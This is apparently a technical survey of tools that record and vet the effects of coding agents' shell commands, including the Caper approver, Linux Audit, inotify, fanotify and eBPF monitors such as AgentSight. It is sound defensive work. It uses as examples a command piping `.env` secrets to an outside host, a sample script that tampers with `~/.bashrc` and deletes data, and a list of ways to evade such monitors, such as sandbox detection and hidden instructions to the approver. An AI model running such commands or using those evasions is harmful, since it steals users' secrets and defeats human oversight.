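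For output and network traffic, Caper also lists the files that the same process had read beforehand, as possible sources of the data. It doesn't link the data to files read by another process. In `cat .env | curl -d @- https://example.com`, for example, `cat` reads the file and `curl` sends it. The report would include both the read and the connection attempt, but the approver would have to link them itself.

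### Testing Caper on SABER and YoloFS-Ext

*SABER* (Hu, Tang and colleagues, 2026) contains 716 tasks, each of which places an agent in a project folder with an ordinary development request that can easily lead to harm. Wu and colleagues used the 682 tasks that need only a shell. In some, a file or a tool's output contains malicious instructions. In others, there is no attacker, but one way of doing the job is destructive, such as resetting a whole database to apply one change. In the rest, the request is dangerous only because of something in the project, such as a note that the database is in production use.

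Wu and colleagues built the second benchmark, YoloFS-Ext, from 13 small projects that Zhong and colleagues used to test their file system, YoloFS. In each of its 102 dangerous tasks, the user asks the agent to run a tool, for example to deploy the project, and the tool does the job but also deletes or overwrites an unrelated file. The harmful code is in a script, a Makefile, a chain of scripts or a compiled program. Each dangerous task has a safe twin with the same request, files and command but harmless code in the tool, so an approver that blocks the command in a twin has made a mistake.

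On SABER, 6.7% of tasks ended in harm with Caper, compared with 19.7% for the same agent without approval and 14.8% to 21.2% with six other systems. On YoloFS-Ext, 7.8% ended in harm with Caper, compared with 71.6% without approval and 35.3% with YoloFS, the best of the other systems. Caper blocked the tool in one of the 102 safe twins (1.0%).

Caper reduced harm on SABER, but the agent also completed fewer tasks safely, 48.6% compared with 57.4% without any approval. Caper blocked at least one command in 78.8% of the tasks. SABER has no safe twins, so the number of unnecessary blocks is unknown. Wu and colleagues also changed SABER's scoring for every system because it had counted some harmless commands as violations, including a text search for "scp", the name of a file-copying program. Under the original rules, Caper's harm rate was 9.0%, still the lowest.

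Wu and colleagues also tested whether the approver needs a real run. They had a model predict each command's effects by reading the command and the files it refers to, following references up to three levels deep. With these predictions, only 3.9% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm, slightly fewer than with observed effects. But the approver also blocked 61.8% of the safe twins, the same share as when it had no information about effects. The predicting model couldn't read compiled programs, and the approver blocked every twin that used one. The approver cleared the harmless tools only when it had the results of a trial run.

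Without the diffs, harm also rose from 7.8% to 13.7%. The increase came from overwritten files, because a report without a diff shows only that such a file's size has changed. The diffs come from Caper's comparison of the project folder, not from the trace.

A report helps only if the approver understands it. Showing the observed effects to a weaker approver model cut wrongly blocked twins from 53.9% to 4.9% but raised harm from 25.5% to 33.3%. The stronger model didn't always do better with more context. When it received only the command and the report, without the user's request or the conversation, 1.0% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm and it blocked no twins. That result is hard to generalize from because the harm in YoloFS-Ext is always damage to a file that the request never mentions. In real projects, the user may want a folder deleted, and the approver can't know that without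 the request.

### Caper's overhead and limits

Caper's sandbox adds about 0.5 seconds to an allowed command and 1.5 seconds to a blocked one. Tracing accounts for a median of only 14 milliseconds of this. Saving the snapshot takes 347 milliseconds, and the two scans of the project folder take 68 and 66 milliseconds. The approver's decision takes longer than all of these steps combined, at a median of 3.2 seconds.

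These numbers come from short commands run without network access, with a median traced run of 81 milliseconds. They don't include a large `npm install`, where the slowdowns that Grayson and colleagues measured for file-heavy programs would matter more. Caper also couldn't have downloaded the packages in its test setup. Wu and colleagues suggest letting the container reach package registries, since a rollback removes anything downloaded into it. For other traffic, they suggest a proxy that records each request and returns a placeholder response.

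Caper checks only shell commands. If the agent plants harmful code with the harness's edit tool, Caper reports the harm when a later command runs the code. An edit that does damage directly, such as overwriting a configuration file, never goes through a trial run. An attacker who knows about Caper could write a program that does no harm when it detects the sandbox, delay the damage, hide instructions to the approver in text that ends up in the report, or spread a harmful change over several innocent-looking commands. Neither benchmark includes such an attacker. Each system ran each task only once, so small differences between the systems may be due to chance.

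### The sample command

A trace with the options shown earlier contains direct evidence of seven of the eight effects of `./setup.sh`, but it can't restore anything. It shows that the script opened `src/config.json` for writing, moved `notes.md`, created and deleted the temporary file, changed `~/.bashrc`, read `.env` and connected to the outside server. It also shows every file that npm wrote.

For `old.db`, the trace stops at `dockerd`'s socket. But it includes the arguments the script passed to `docker`, so a reader might find the folder `/srv/data` and an instruction to delete the file. This is evidence of what the script requested, and the deletion could still have failed.

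The process that writes `cache.bin` is a descendant of the script, so `-f` keeps following it after the shell exits. strace doesn't finish until every process it follows has ended, so the tool call that normally returns at "Setup complete" now waits for the background process. If the harness stops waiting and terminates strace, then with plain `-f` the process may continue untraced and write `cache.bin` with no entry in the log. With `--seccomp-bpf`, the kernel kills the process when strace exits, and the file may never appear.

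Under Caper, npm couldn't download the package that changes `~/.bashrc` because it would have no network, and `old.db` would not be deleted because the script couldn't connect to `dockerd`. The approver would still receive the new contents of `src/config.json`, the read of `.env` and the failed connection attempts. If Caper let npm reach its registry, the raw trace would include the write to `~/.bashrc`, but the effects report might not, because Caper compares only the project folder. If the approver blocked the script for another reason, the rollback would still remove the added line, because the snapshot covers the container's whole file system.

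## Linux Audit, inotify and fanotify

strace records only the commands it starts and their descendants, and it has to stop them to do so. Linux also has three built-in facilities that can record activity anywhere on the machine without a tracer. Linux Audit logs the system calls that match an administrator's rules. inotify and fanotify notify a program when other programs open, change or delete files. None of the three saves a file's old contents, so they can show that `src/config.json` changed but can't bring back the earlier version.

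### From an Audit rule to a log entry

Linux Audit is meant for servers whose operators must be able to prove who did what. According to SUSE's *Understanding Linux audit*, some security certifications under the Common Criteria, an international standard, require such a log. A record takes this route:

1. An administrator loads rules with the `auditctl` program, or lists them in a file that the system reads at startup.
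2. A program makes a system call. The kernel notes the details of the call on entry and then carries it out.
3. When the call ends, the kernel compares it with the rules in order and stops at the first match. A rule with the action `always` produces an event, and a rule with `never` suppresses it.
4. The kernel places the event's records in a queue in its own memory.
5. auditd, a permanently running service, reads the queue and appends the records to `/var/log/audit/audit.log`.

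The kernel decides whether to log a system call when the call ends, so the log includes the result as well as the request. Only an administrator can load rules or delete the logs, so an agent without those rights can't erase its record the way it can erase a shadow repository. An administrator can also lock the rules until the next restart.

On many systems, a default rule turns auditing off. According to the manual page *auditctl(8)* (Grubb, 2023), auditd often installs this rule, which makes every new process skip all rule checks. Rules added later load without an error but match nothing until the administrator removes the default rule.

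### A rule set for an agent

Suppose the agent has its own account with user ID 1500 and the home folder `/home/agent`, and the project is in `/home/agent/app`. A small rule set could look like this:

```
-b 8192
-a always,exit -F arch=b64 -F dir=/home/agent -F perm=wa -F auid=1500 -F key=agent-write
-a always,exit -F arch=b64 -F path=/home/agent/app/.env -F perm=r -F auid=1500 -F key=agent-secret
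-a always,exit -F arch=b64 -S execve,execveat -F auid=1500 -F key=agent-exec
-a always,exit -F arch=b64 -S connect -F auid=1500 -F key=agent-net
-a always,exit -F arch=b64 -F dir=/srv/data -F perm=wa -F key=shared-data
```

The `-b` line sets the queue length. In the other lines, `always,exit` makes the kernel log matching calls when they end, and `auid=1500` limits a rule to processes from the agent's login. The key is a label investigators can search for with `ausearch`.

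The `agent-write` rule covers the whole home folder. `perm=wa` selects the system calls that write to a file or change its attributes, such as its permissions. Audit doesn't log individual `write` calls, because they would overwhelm the log. It checks whether the process asked for write access when it opened the file. The log therefore shows that a process opened `src/config.json` for writing, but not whether it wrote anything or how much.

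The rule for `.env` names one file because Audit doesn't support wildcards in paths. Each new project therefore needs its own rule. A rule for reads of the whole home folder would cover every `.env` file, but it would also log the thousands of files Node.js opens while npm runs.

According to Grubb's *audit.rules(7)* (2023), a rule for a folder includes everything below it except other mounted file systems. `/tmp` is outside the home folder, so temporary files there need their own rule. A rule with `arch=b64` covers only 64-bit system calls, so the administrator needs a second copy with `arch=b32` to cover 32-bit programs.

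Programs can also bypass these rules with io_uring, a newer interface that lets them request file and network operations from the kernel without making a separate system call for each. Audit checks io_uring operations against a separate list of rules, so catching file opens made this way requires adding a line such as `-a always,io_uring -S openat,openat2 -F key=agent-uring`.

### Reading one event

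When `setup.sh` runs `mv notes.md docs/notes.md`, the `agent-exec` rule matches the start of the `mv` program. The event, without some of its fields, would look like this:

```
type=SYSCALL msg=audit(1796468400.120:5120): arch=c000003e syscall=59 success=yes exit=0 items=2 ppid=4102 pid=4103 auid=1500 uid=1500 ses=12 comm="mv" exe="/usr/bin/mv" key="agent-exec"
type=EXECVE msg=audit(1796468400.120:5120): argc=3 a0="mv" a1="notes.md" a2="docs/notes.md"
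type=CWD msg=audit(1796468400.120:5120): cwd="/home/agent/app"
type=PATH msg=audit(1796468400.120:5120): item=0 name="/usr/bin/mv" inode=917650 mode=0100755 ouid=0 nametype=NORMAL
type=PATH msg=audit(1796468400.120:5120): item=1 name="/lib64/ld-linux-x86-64.so.2" inode=918022 mode=0100755 ouid=0 nametype=NORMAL
```

All five records share a time stamp, in seconds since 1970, and the serial number 5120. An investigator needs these to reassemble the event, since records from different processes can be interleaved in the log.

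The SYSCALL record describes the call and the process that made it. On a 64-bit Intel or AMD processor, call number 59 is `execve`, which loads a program. `ppid=4102` is the shell running the script, and `pid=4103` is the process that became `mv`. `auid` and `ses` identify the login the process belongs to.

The EXECVE record contains the argument count and the arguments, which makes it the most useful record for a command such as `docker run`.

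The CWD record gives the process's working directory. SUSE explains that Audit logs a path as the program supplied it, so a reader has to combine a relative path such as `notes.md` with this directory to get the full path. Each file involved in the call has its own PATH record, in this case one for the `mv` program and one for the loader.

A full event usually ends with a PROCTITLE record, which contains the command line in hexadecimal. According to Red Hat's *Understanding Audit log files*, the encoding prevents users from influencing the programs that read the log. Without it, an attacker could start a program with an argument that looks like part of another record.

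This event shows only that `mv` started. The move itself matches the `agent-write` rule and produces a second event, with PATH records that mark the old name as deleted and the new one as created. Both records have the same inode number, which identifies the operation as a move.

### Attribution by login

When someone logs in, the system gives their first process a login user ID (`auid`) and a session ID (`ses`), which all its descendants inherit. The login user ID stays the same when a process switches accounts, for example with `su` or `sudo`. If an agent logged in as user 1500 runs a script that installs a system package as root, the log shows `uid=0` and `auid=1500`.

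Attribution by login user ID and session ID is simpler than rebuilding a process tree, because each event already contains both IDs. The process that writes `cache.bin` keeps them after the shell exits and the kernel gives it a new parent.

Most developers start their agent in a terminal in their desktop session. The editor, the browser and the agent then have the same login user ID (`auid`) and often the same session ID (`ses`), so an Audit rule for that login records all of them. To be recorded separately, the agent needs its own login. A separate account gives it a different `auid`. A second login to the developer's account, for example over local SSH, gives it a different `ses`, which Audit rules can also filter on. If the harness logged in again for every shell command, each tool call would get its own session ID.

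Starting the agent with `sudo -u agent` isn't enough, because the login user ID would still be the developer's. A rule could filter on the ordinary user ID instead, but that ID changes when a script uses `sudo`.

A separate account has a side benefit. `~/.bashrc` then means the agent's own file, and the malicious line never reaches the developer's terminal.

Services that start with the machine have no login, so Audit marks their login user ID as unset, which the log shows as 4294967295. `dockerd` is such a service, and the processes in its containers inherit the unset value. The rules with `auid=1500` don't match the deletion of `old.db`, and they would record nothing useful about an agent whose harness runs its commands in a Docker container.

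For this reason, the last rule in the set has no `auid` filter. It logs the deletion of `old.db` no matter who deletes it, but nothing in the event links the deletion to the agent.

### When the queue fills

The kernel's audit queue holds 64 records by default. Grubb (2006), in *audit_set_backlog_limit(3)*, warns that bursts of activity can overrun it. `npm install` creates thousands of files, each of which generates several records.

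When the queue is full, the kernel first waits for auditd to catch up, by default for up to 60 seconds. The program that caused the event stalls during the wait, so a user may notice a slow command before Audit loses anything. If there is still no room, the kernel's response depends on a setting called the failure mode. By default, it writes a warning to the system log and carries on. An administrator can instead set it to discard the records silently or halt the machine. Grubb suggests halting for secure environments, but SUSE points out that the machine then stops without saving the latest log entries to disk. Few developers would accept this setting on their laptops, since a routine command such as `npm install` could trigger a halt.

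The kernel counts the records it discards. The command `auditctl -s` prints this count as `lost`, along with the number of records waiting in the queue. A harness with administrator rights could reset the count to zero before each shell command and read it afterwards. If the count is still zero, the queue lost no records. Otherwise, some records are missing, but they may not be the agent's, because the count covers the whole machine.

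The counter also leaves out records that auditd has received and then deleted. In SUSE's default configuration, auditd keeps five log files of 8 MB each and overwrites the oldest. Red Hat's example event, a single failed attempt to open a file, is roughly 800 characters, so 40 MB holds about 50,000 such events. One or two large installs could push the start of a long agent session out of the log. The same configuration stops logging when the disk is full.

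An administrator can reduce the volume with a `never` rule for npm's download cache, placed above the other rules so the kernel reaches it first. Audit would then not record what a malicious package does in that folder.

Audit can also be slow. The kernel checks every system-call rule whenever any program makes a system call, so Grubb advises combining rules and restricting them to particular folders where possible. *Are we there yet?* (Dong, Li and colleagues, 2023) reports that Audit added up to 821% to running time. Houssel and colleagues consider it better suited to targeted audits than to continuous capture of a whole system.

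### inotify

inotify is the facility that programs such as code editors and development servers typically use to notice that a file has changed. It needs no administrator rights. A program asks the kernel to watch a file or folder and then reads events from a queue. An event contains the number of the watch, the kind of change and usually the file's name within the folder.

According to *inotify(7)*, a watch on a folder doesn't extend to its subfolders. A recorder therefore has to set up a watch for every folder in a project, which can take a long time in a large `node_modules`. The kernel also limits the number of watches per user.

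The larger problem is folders that don't exist yet. Suppose npm installs the package esbuild while a recorder is watching `node_modules`:

1. npm creates the folder `node_modules/esbuild`, and the kernel queues an event for it.
2. npm writes several files into the new folder. There is no watch on it yet, so these writes produce no events.
3. The recorder reads the first event and adds a watch for the new folder.

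The manual advises programs to scan a new folder immediately after adding the watch. The scan finds the files that npm wrote, but not a file that an install script created and deleted before the watch was added. The same delay occurs at every level of nested folders.

If the queue fills up, the kernel drops further events and adds a single overflow event. This event doesn't identify what was dropped, so the recorder has to scan the project again. The kernel also merges consecutive identical events, so there can be fewer events than writes.

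A move produces two events, one for the old folder and one for the new, with a shared number that lets the recorder pair them. Other events can come between the two. If the file moves to a folder without a watch, the second event never arrives, and the move is hard to distinguish from one that takes the file out of the watched area altogether.

inotify gives no information about the process or user behind an event. A recorder can't even separate its own file accesses from those of other programs. On a laptop where a code formatter runs whenever the user saves a file, the log would mix the formatter's changes with those of `setup.sh`, without any field to sort them by.

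inotify is therefore weak evidence on its own, but it could make a state comparison cheaper. A harness could keep watches on the project and, after each command, compare only the folders in which something happened. The manual itself recommends occasional checks against the actual files, because missed events can leave a program with a wrong picture of the folder.

### fanotify

fanotify, which Linux has had since version 2.6.37, removes several of these limits for programs with administrator rights. Its typical users are virus scanners. Instead of watching single folders, a program can mark a whole file system, and *fanotify(7)* confirms that this covers the entire tree without the race over new folders. A mark on a file system also catches changes made through another mount of it. If a container has `/srv/data` attached under a different name, the recorder still gets an event for the deletion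 of `old.db`.

Each event includes the ID of the process that caused it, but not the parent process or login user ID. To attribute the event more fully, the recorder has to look these up while the process still exists. An install script that runs for a few milliseconds may exit before the recorder reads the event, leaving only the process ID.

fanotify can't fill that gap by recording program starts. It can report that a process opened a file in order to execute it, but according to *fanotify_mark(2)*, it doesn't do so when an interpreter reads the file. For `bash setup.sh`, the recorder learns that `bash` started, but not that it was running `setup.sh`.

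Linux added events for created, deleted and moved files to fanotify in version 5.1. Since version 5.17, a program can also request a single rename event that contains both the old and new names, so it doesn't have to match separate move events.

The kernel can also wait for the listener's permission before it lets a process open or read a file. When `setup.sh` opens `src/config.json`, for instance:

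1. The kernel pauses the script and sends a permission event to the listener.
2. The listener examines the file and answers "allow" or "deny".
3. The kernel either opens the file or returns an error to the script.

As with the stops under `ptrace`, a recorder could use this pause to copy the old contents of `src/config.json`, but this would be awkward. The event doesn't show whether the process is going to read or write, so the recorder would also have to copy files that programs only read. Deleting or renaming a file doesn't trigger a permission event, so the recorder wouldn't get a chance to copy `old.db` before it was deleted. A program that needs both permission events and events for deletions or renames has to set up two listeners, because the kernel doesn't let one listener receive both. If the recorder crashes, the kernel allows all pending requests.

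fanotify has a queue too. Before Linux 5.13 it held 16,384 events, and administrators can now set the limit. As with inotify, the kernel reports an overflow but not what it dropped. A listener with administrator rights can ask for a queue without a limit, at the cost of memory. Handling overflow is up to whoever writes the recorder, and one of the example programs in the manual page simply ignores it.

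According to their manual pages, fanotify and inotify do not report reads or changes that a program makes through a memory-mapped file. The recorder still gets an event when the program opens the file, and another when the program closes a file it opened for writing. But the program can close the file and keep changing it through the mapping, so a recorder that reads the file at the closing event may miss later changes. Linux Audit logs when a program opens a file with write access, which at least identifies the file as one that may have changed.

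Without administrator rights, fanotify offers little more than inotify. According to *fanotify_init(2)*, an ordinary user can't mark a file system, request permission events or see the process ID behind another program's event. A harness running as an ordinary user on a developer's laptop would therefore need an administrator to install a helper to use these features.

### Why agent monitors have chosen another method

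Two recent monitors built for agents, AgentSight (by Zheng and colleagues) and *Agent-Warden* (2026), record in the kernel using eBPF rather than Audit, inotify or fanotify. eBPF lets an administrator load small programs into the running kernel. *Agent-Warden* tracks which agent processes handled which files. It mentions Audit only as the basis of early systems for tracing the history of files and processes.

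One reason is that Audit can filter only on fields built into the kernel. Houssel and colleagues explain that changes to such built-in systems must pass a long review, so tools that need finer filtering record too much and discard the surplus afterwards. Selecting one container's events is a typical case.

A team that can't load its own code into the kernel could still get a usable log from Audit. The team would need a separate login for the agent, a longer queue and someone to maintain the rules.

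### The sample command

Suppose an administrator has loaded the rule set above and the script's temporary file is in the project folder. inotify has watches on all existing folders in the project, on the home folder and on `/srv/data`. fanotify runs with administrator rights and has a mark on the file system that holds all these folders.

| Effect | Linux Audit | inotify | fanotify |
|---|---|---|---|
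| 1. `src/config.json` overwritten | Opened for writing, with process and login | Modified | Modified, with process ID |
| 2. `notes.md` moved | One event with both names | Two events with a shared number | One event with both names and process ID |
| 3. Temporary file | Created and deleted | Created and deleted | Created and deleted, with process ID |
| 4. Line added to `~/.bashrc` | Opened for writing, with process and login | Modified | Modified, with process ID |
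| 5. `.env` read | Opened for reading | Opened and read | Opened and read, with process ID |
| 6. HTTPS request | Connection attempt with address | Nothing | Nothing |
| 7. `old.db` deleted | `docker` command; deletion without a login | Deletion | Deletion, with process ID |
| 8. `cache.bin` written later | Opened for writing, with process and login | Created and modified | Created and modified, with process ID |

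All three work independently of the tool call, so if the harness returns "Setup complete" while the background process is still running, the recorder will still capture `cache.bin` when it appears.

Only Audit provides a way to trace the write to `~/.bashrc` back to npm. Each event includes the parent's process ID, which can be matched to a program name using the program starts logged under `agent-exec`. The chain can break where a shell forks a copy of itself to run part of a script, because the copy loads no new program and the rule set doesn't log `fork`. Even then, the login user ID links the write to the agent.

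The HTTPS request may look like a failure in the Audit log, because Audit treats `EINPROGRESS` as an error and logs the pending connection as `success=no`. Adding `success=1` to the `agent-net` rule to reduce noise would therefore drop many successful connections from the log.

The Audit log contains an event with `auid=1500` for the start of `docker`, including its arguments, and a later event with an unset `auid` for the process that deleted `old.db`. An investigator can connect the two events by their times and by the path in the arguments. If other containers were using `/srv/data` at the same moment, the connection would be only a guess.

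## eBPF monitors such as Tetragon, Falco, Tracee and AgentSight

Unlike Linux Audit, an eBPF monitor can load its own filter into the kernel. eBPF stands for extended Berkeley Packet Filter, because engineers first used the technique to inspect network packets. Tetragon from Isovalent, Tracee from Aqua Security and Falco, a Cloud Native Computing Foundation project, are security tools for Linux servers that use eBPF to record program, file and network activity. AgentSight applies it to coding agents.

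### How an eBPF program works

Faulty code inside the kernel can crash the whole machine, so the kernel checks each eBPF program before it runs. For a monitor that logs file writes, the steps are:

1. The monitor asks the kernel to load a program, which by default requires administrator rights.
2. A part of the kernel called the verifier analyzes the program. According to *Agent-Warden*, it rejects the program unless it can establish, among other things, that the program's loops end and that it accesses only valid memory.
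3. The kernel attaches the program to a chosen point, such as the function that checks whether a process may write to a file.
4. Each time any process reaches that point, the kernel runs the program. The program can read the process ID and the file's path, and it ignores events that don't match its filter.
5. For a matching event, the program puts a record in a ring buffer, a fixed-size area of memory that it shares with the monitor.
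6. The monitor, which runs in user space (outside the kernel, like any ordinary program), reads the record and writes it to a log.

eBPF programs can keep data between events in tables called maps, for example a list of the agent's processes. Unlike under strace, the recorded process never waits for the monitor. But new records are lost as soon as the buffer is full, whereas Audit first makes the process wait.

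### Attaching to system calls, kernel functions and security hooks

The kernel has fixed attachment points, called tracepoints, at the entry and exit of system calls, and they change little between kernel versions. At the entry of a call that deletes a file, an eBPF program can read the path, but the result is available only at the exit. A monitor therefore usually attaches one program to each, saves the arguments in a map at the entry and completes the record at the exit. If it used only the entry, its log would include deletions that the kernel refused.

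Falco used to send two events for every system call, one on entry and one on exit. Version 0.42 removed the entry events, and the exit event now carries the arguments as well. This change lost the program's file name for successful `execve` calls, because they replace the memory that held it. Version 0.43 restored the file name.

A kprobe attaches an eBPF program to almost any kernel function, where it can read data the kernel has already processed, such as the full path behind a file descriptor. But kernel functions change between versions, so a kprobe that works on one machine may fail on another. Fentry and fexit probes, a newer type, attach to the same functions with less overhead. Uprobes attach eBPF programs to functions in ordinary programs and libraries.

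The third kind of attachment uses security hooks. Before a sensitive operation, the kernel calls each of its security modules, such as SELinux, in turn to check whether to allow it. An eBPF program can join this chain as a Linux Security Module (LSM) program. Houssel and colleagues put theirs last, so the kernel ran it only for operations that all the other modules had allowed. A single program could therefore provide both the arguments and the verdict, which gave this type the lowest overhead in their tests when they included the work of getting the verdict. An LSM program also reads the kernel's own copy of the arguments, which the calling program can't change.

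The verdict only determines whether an operation is permitted. The operation can still fail after the last hook, for example because the disk is full or a server refuses the connection. *Agent-Warden* therefore reads the return value and the number of bytes transferred before it records a read or write. Houssel and colleagues also call it an open question whether the hooks cover every way that data moves between processes and files.

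Since Linux 6.0, an LSM program can attach to a single cgroup, a group of processes that the kernel manages together. Every Docker container has its own cgroup, and a new process starts in its parent's cgroup. If a harness started its shells in a separate cgroup, the kernel would run the program for the agent's processes, including background processes that outlive their shell, but not for the developer's other programs, such as an editor or browser.

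### What Tetragon, Falco and Tracee record

By default, Tetragon logs the start and end of programs across the machine. The start event contains the program's path, arguments, working folder and user, and the same details for its parent. For `./setup.sh`, the log would contain `mv notes.md docs/notes.md`, `npm install` and the full `docker` command. Arguments can include passwords, so Tetragon can replace text matching a pattern with asterisks before it exports an event. Tetragon needs a tracing policy to log file and network events. This is a configuration file that specifies what to attach to and how to filter.

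Falco checks events against a set of rules and issues an alert when one matches, so by default it doesn't log ordinary activity. Overwriting `src/config.json` would normally leave no trace. Version 0.44, released in May 2026, added a rule relevant to agents that reports network tools, such as `curl`, started from an install script of npm or a similar package manager. The package in the sample command wouldn't trigger this rule because it only adds a line to `~/.bashrc`. Falco can also record system calls when a rule matches, for 5 seconds by default, if an administrator turns this on.

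Tracee users select events by name, from single events such as `execve` to broad sets such as all system calls. Aqua Security recommends specific events over broad sets.

To attribute an event to an agent, each tool has to track which process started which. Process IDs alone aren't enough because the kernel reuses them and a process keeps its ID when it loads a different program. Tetragon's *Concepts* gives an example in which bash replaces itself with `curl`, so both have the ID 52699. Tetragon gives each program start its own identifier, which encodes the machine's name, a start time and the process ID. Each event also contains the parent's identifier, so a reader can trace a write back to the harness.

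Falco keeps a table of processes in user space, which it fills at startup and updates from the event stream. If an entry is missing, typically because events were dropped, Falco looks it up. It used to do this only by reading `/proc`, the directory where Linux exposes information about running processes, but version 0.44 added a faster lookup inside the kernel.

According to Aqua Security's *Process Tree Data*, Tracee's optional process tree identifies each process by a hash of its start time and thread ID, and holds up to 16,384 processes by default. When the tree is full, it discards the least recently used entries. Tracee can also query `/proc` to fill gaps, but Aqua Security warns that these queries use resources and can cause further losses.

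None of these lookups can recover information about a process that has already exited. If a monitor loses the start event of a short-lived install script, it may never record that the script connected npm to the process that changed `~/.bashrc`.

### Filtering and dropped events

Tetragon applies its policies inside the kernel, so events that don't match never enter the buffer. A policy can filter by path, program, process ID and other properties. Tracee can also filter by process, program, container or user in the kernel, and its older documentation describes a `--scope tree=` option that limits recording to the descendants of one process.

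Falco does most of its filtering in user space. It captures the system calls its rules need, plus those it needs to maintain its process table. In the documentation's example, a rule about program starts needs 2 system calls, and the table needs 16 more. The Falco project gives two reasons for not moving the rest of the filtering into the kernel. An eBPF program runs while the application waits, so a complicated filter slows the application down. The eBPF program also has only the raw arguments of one call, which are hard to relate to earlier events. The drawback of filtering in user space is that a single thread must process every event the kernel passes on.

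All three tools report losses:

- Tetragon has a counter for events that the kernel failed to send and another for events lost in its own queue afterwards.
- Falco counts drops by category, such as process creation, program starts, file opens and connections. An administrator can also choose what happens after a drop. According to Falco's *Actions For Dropped System Call Events*, the choices are to ignore it, log a message, issue an alert or stop Falco.
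- Tracee logs a warning that events were dropped because a buffer overflowed. Aqua Security's suggested remedies are a larger buffer and filters for busy paths such as `/tmp`, which would also hide the script's temporary file if it were there.

Falco's categories of lost events matter more than the total, because a lost file event leaves one gap, while a lost process-creation event can detach a whole branch of the process tree from the agent. Falco's rough guide, drawn from its users, is that fewer than 1,000 events per second per processor core are usually harmless and more than 3,000 are harder to handle. These are long-run rates, so they may not apply to the short burst of events from a busy `npm install`.

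### A Tetragon policy for an agent's file writes

The policy below logs file writes by a harness installed at `/usr/local/bin/agent` and by everything it starts. It is based on Tetragon's example policy *filename_monitoring.yaml*.

```yaml
apiVersion: cilium.io/v1alpha1
kind: TracingPolicy
metadata:
  name: "agent-file-writes"
spec:
  kprobes:
  - call: "security_file_permission"
    syscall: false
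    return: true
    args:
    - index: 0
      type: "file"
    - index: 1
      type: "int"
    returnArg:
      index: 0
      type: "int"
    returnArgAction: "Post"
    selectors:
    - matchBinaries:
      - operator: "In"
        values:
        - "/usr/local/bin/agent"
        followChildren: true
      matchArgs:
      - index: 0
        operator: "Prefix"
        values:
        - "/home/"
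        - "/tmp/"
        - "/etc/"
      - index: 1
        operator: "Equal"
        values:
        - "2"
```

The policy attaches a kprobe to `security_file_permission`, the kernel function that calls the security modules to check each read or write. The function's first argument is the file and its second is the kind of access, where 2 means writing. Tetragon also records the return value, which is 0 if the modules allowed the access. `followChildren` extends the filter from the harness to its descendants. The path prefixes exclude writes to terminals and pipes, which pass through the same function.

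Isovalent's *File Monitoring with eBPF and Tetragon (Part 1)* warns readers not to try the policy without the filters, because it would produce an event for every file access on the machine.

An event contains the path, the process and its parent's identifier, but not the data. A single command can produce several events, such as the two that `echo foo >> /etc/bar` produces in Tetragon's documentation. A rate limit would reduce the volume, but it could also hide changes. According to Tetragon's *Selectors*, the limit treats events from one thread as repeats if the first 40 bytes of each inspected argument are the same. Many files in a deep `node_modules` folder have paths that share their first 40 bytes.

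The administrator has to load the policy before the agent starts, because `followChildren` doesn't match children that already exist. If the harness is a Node.js script, its program path is the path of `node`, so the policy would log every Node.js program on the machine. The log also includes the harness's own writes, such as its transcript.

The policy records only ordinary writes. Tetragon's example also attaches to `security_mmap_file`, which covers files mapped into memory. Moves and deletions would need probes on other functions, such as `security_inode_rename` and `security_inode_unlink`. To record reads of `.env`, an administrator could add a second selector for paths ending in `/.env` with access type 4 (read). That selector would cover every project, whereas Audit needs a rule for each file.

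### How AgentSight links a tool call to kernel events

A Tetragon log shows that npm changed a file, but not which request to the agent led to the change. The Falco project's Prempti, released in May 2026, applies Falco rules to the tool calls that the agent declares. CNCF's *Introducing Prempti* (2026) explains that if an agent compiles a program and runs it, Prempti records the two commands but not what the program did. CNCF recommends Falco's kernel monitoring for recording the program's behavior. AgentSight records both the agent's activity and its effects on the system, and tries to connect them.

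The harness exchanges messages with the model over an encrypted connection, but it encrypts and decrypts them inside its own process. It passes readable text to the library function `SSL_write` and gets the decrypted reply from `SSL_read`. AgentSight attaches uprobes to both functions and copies the text there, so it needs neither a proxy nor any change to the agent. The reply arrives in small pieces, which AgentSight reassembles.

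This depends on finding the functions. Claude Code and programs that run on Node.js contain their own copy of the encryption library instead of using the system's. AgentSight's `record` command, which starts the agent and monitors it, searches the program file for the functions. To monitor a Claude Code session that is already running, the user has to supply the program's path.

For the sample command, the link would form like this:

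1. The uprobe on `SSL_read` captures a reply containing a tool call with the command `./setup.sh`.
2. The harness starts a shell. An eBPF program that tracks process creation adds it to the agent's process tree, because its parent is the harness.
3. AgentSight compares the new process with recent replies. The shell descends from the harness (lineage), it started shortly after the reply (time), and its arguments contain `./setup.sh` (argument matching). The time window is 100 to 500 milliseconds.
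4. The shell starts npm and other programs. Their file and network events belong to the same branch of the tree.
5. A second language model reads the combined record, explains what happened and assigns a confidence score.

Each of the three signals can fail in ordinary use, so Zheng and colleagues go too far when they write that together the signals definitively establish cause and effect. If Claude Code asks for permission and the user takes ten seconds to answer, the shell starts after the window has closed. Argument matching connects the reply to the shell, but it misses the script's write to `~/.bashrc` because the command `./setup.sh` doesn't mention that file. Lineage covers that write, even if npm makes it two minutes later, but not the deletion of `old.db` by a container. Zheng and colleagues don't specify how AgentSight decides when the signals disagree.

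### Two agents at once

If a developer has two Claude Code sessions open in separate terminals and both models request `npm test` at the same moment, AgentSight can't tell the two calls apart by time or arguments. But each reply passes through a different harness process, and each shell is a child of the harness that started it. AgentSight can therefore match each reply to the right shell, as long as it keeps the process ID with each reply.

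Matching replies to shells is harder when two subagents share a session and the harness runs both in a single process, because that process receives both replies and is the parent of both shells. Suppose one subagent calls `./setup.sh` and the other calls `make test` 80 milliseconds later. Both shells may start within 500 milliseconds of both replies, so only the arguments show which shell belongs to which reply. If both subagents instead call `npm test` in different folders, the parent process, timing and arguments all fit either pairing, and AgentSight could not reliably match each reply to its shell.

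A wrong guess about which subagent's request started a shell affects everything below that shell. The events from one `npm test` would stay together, because lineage still connects them to their shell, but they would all appear under the other subagent's request. A harness could prevent this by logging the process ID of the shell it starts for each tool call.

Even correct matching wouldn't always identify the subagent responsible. If one subagent edits a Makefile and another runs `make`, any resulting deletions come from the second subagent's process tree, even though the first subagent wrote the command that caused them. *Agent-Warden* addresses this by tracking which processes read files that the agent's processes wrote.

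### AgentSight's case studies and overhead

Zheng and colleagues came close to this test when they monitored six Claude Code subagents working together on a software project. From the 3,153 events left after AgentSight's matching, they found that some subagents, such as those for the frontend and the tests, had to wait for each other and repeatedly retried when another held a lock on a file. They concluded that a clearer division of roles could save time and tokens. They didn't report how many events AgentSight linked to the wrong subagent, so the case shows the record was useful but not how accurate it was.

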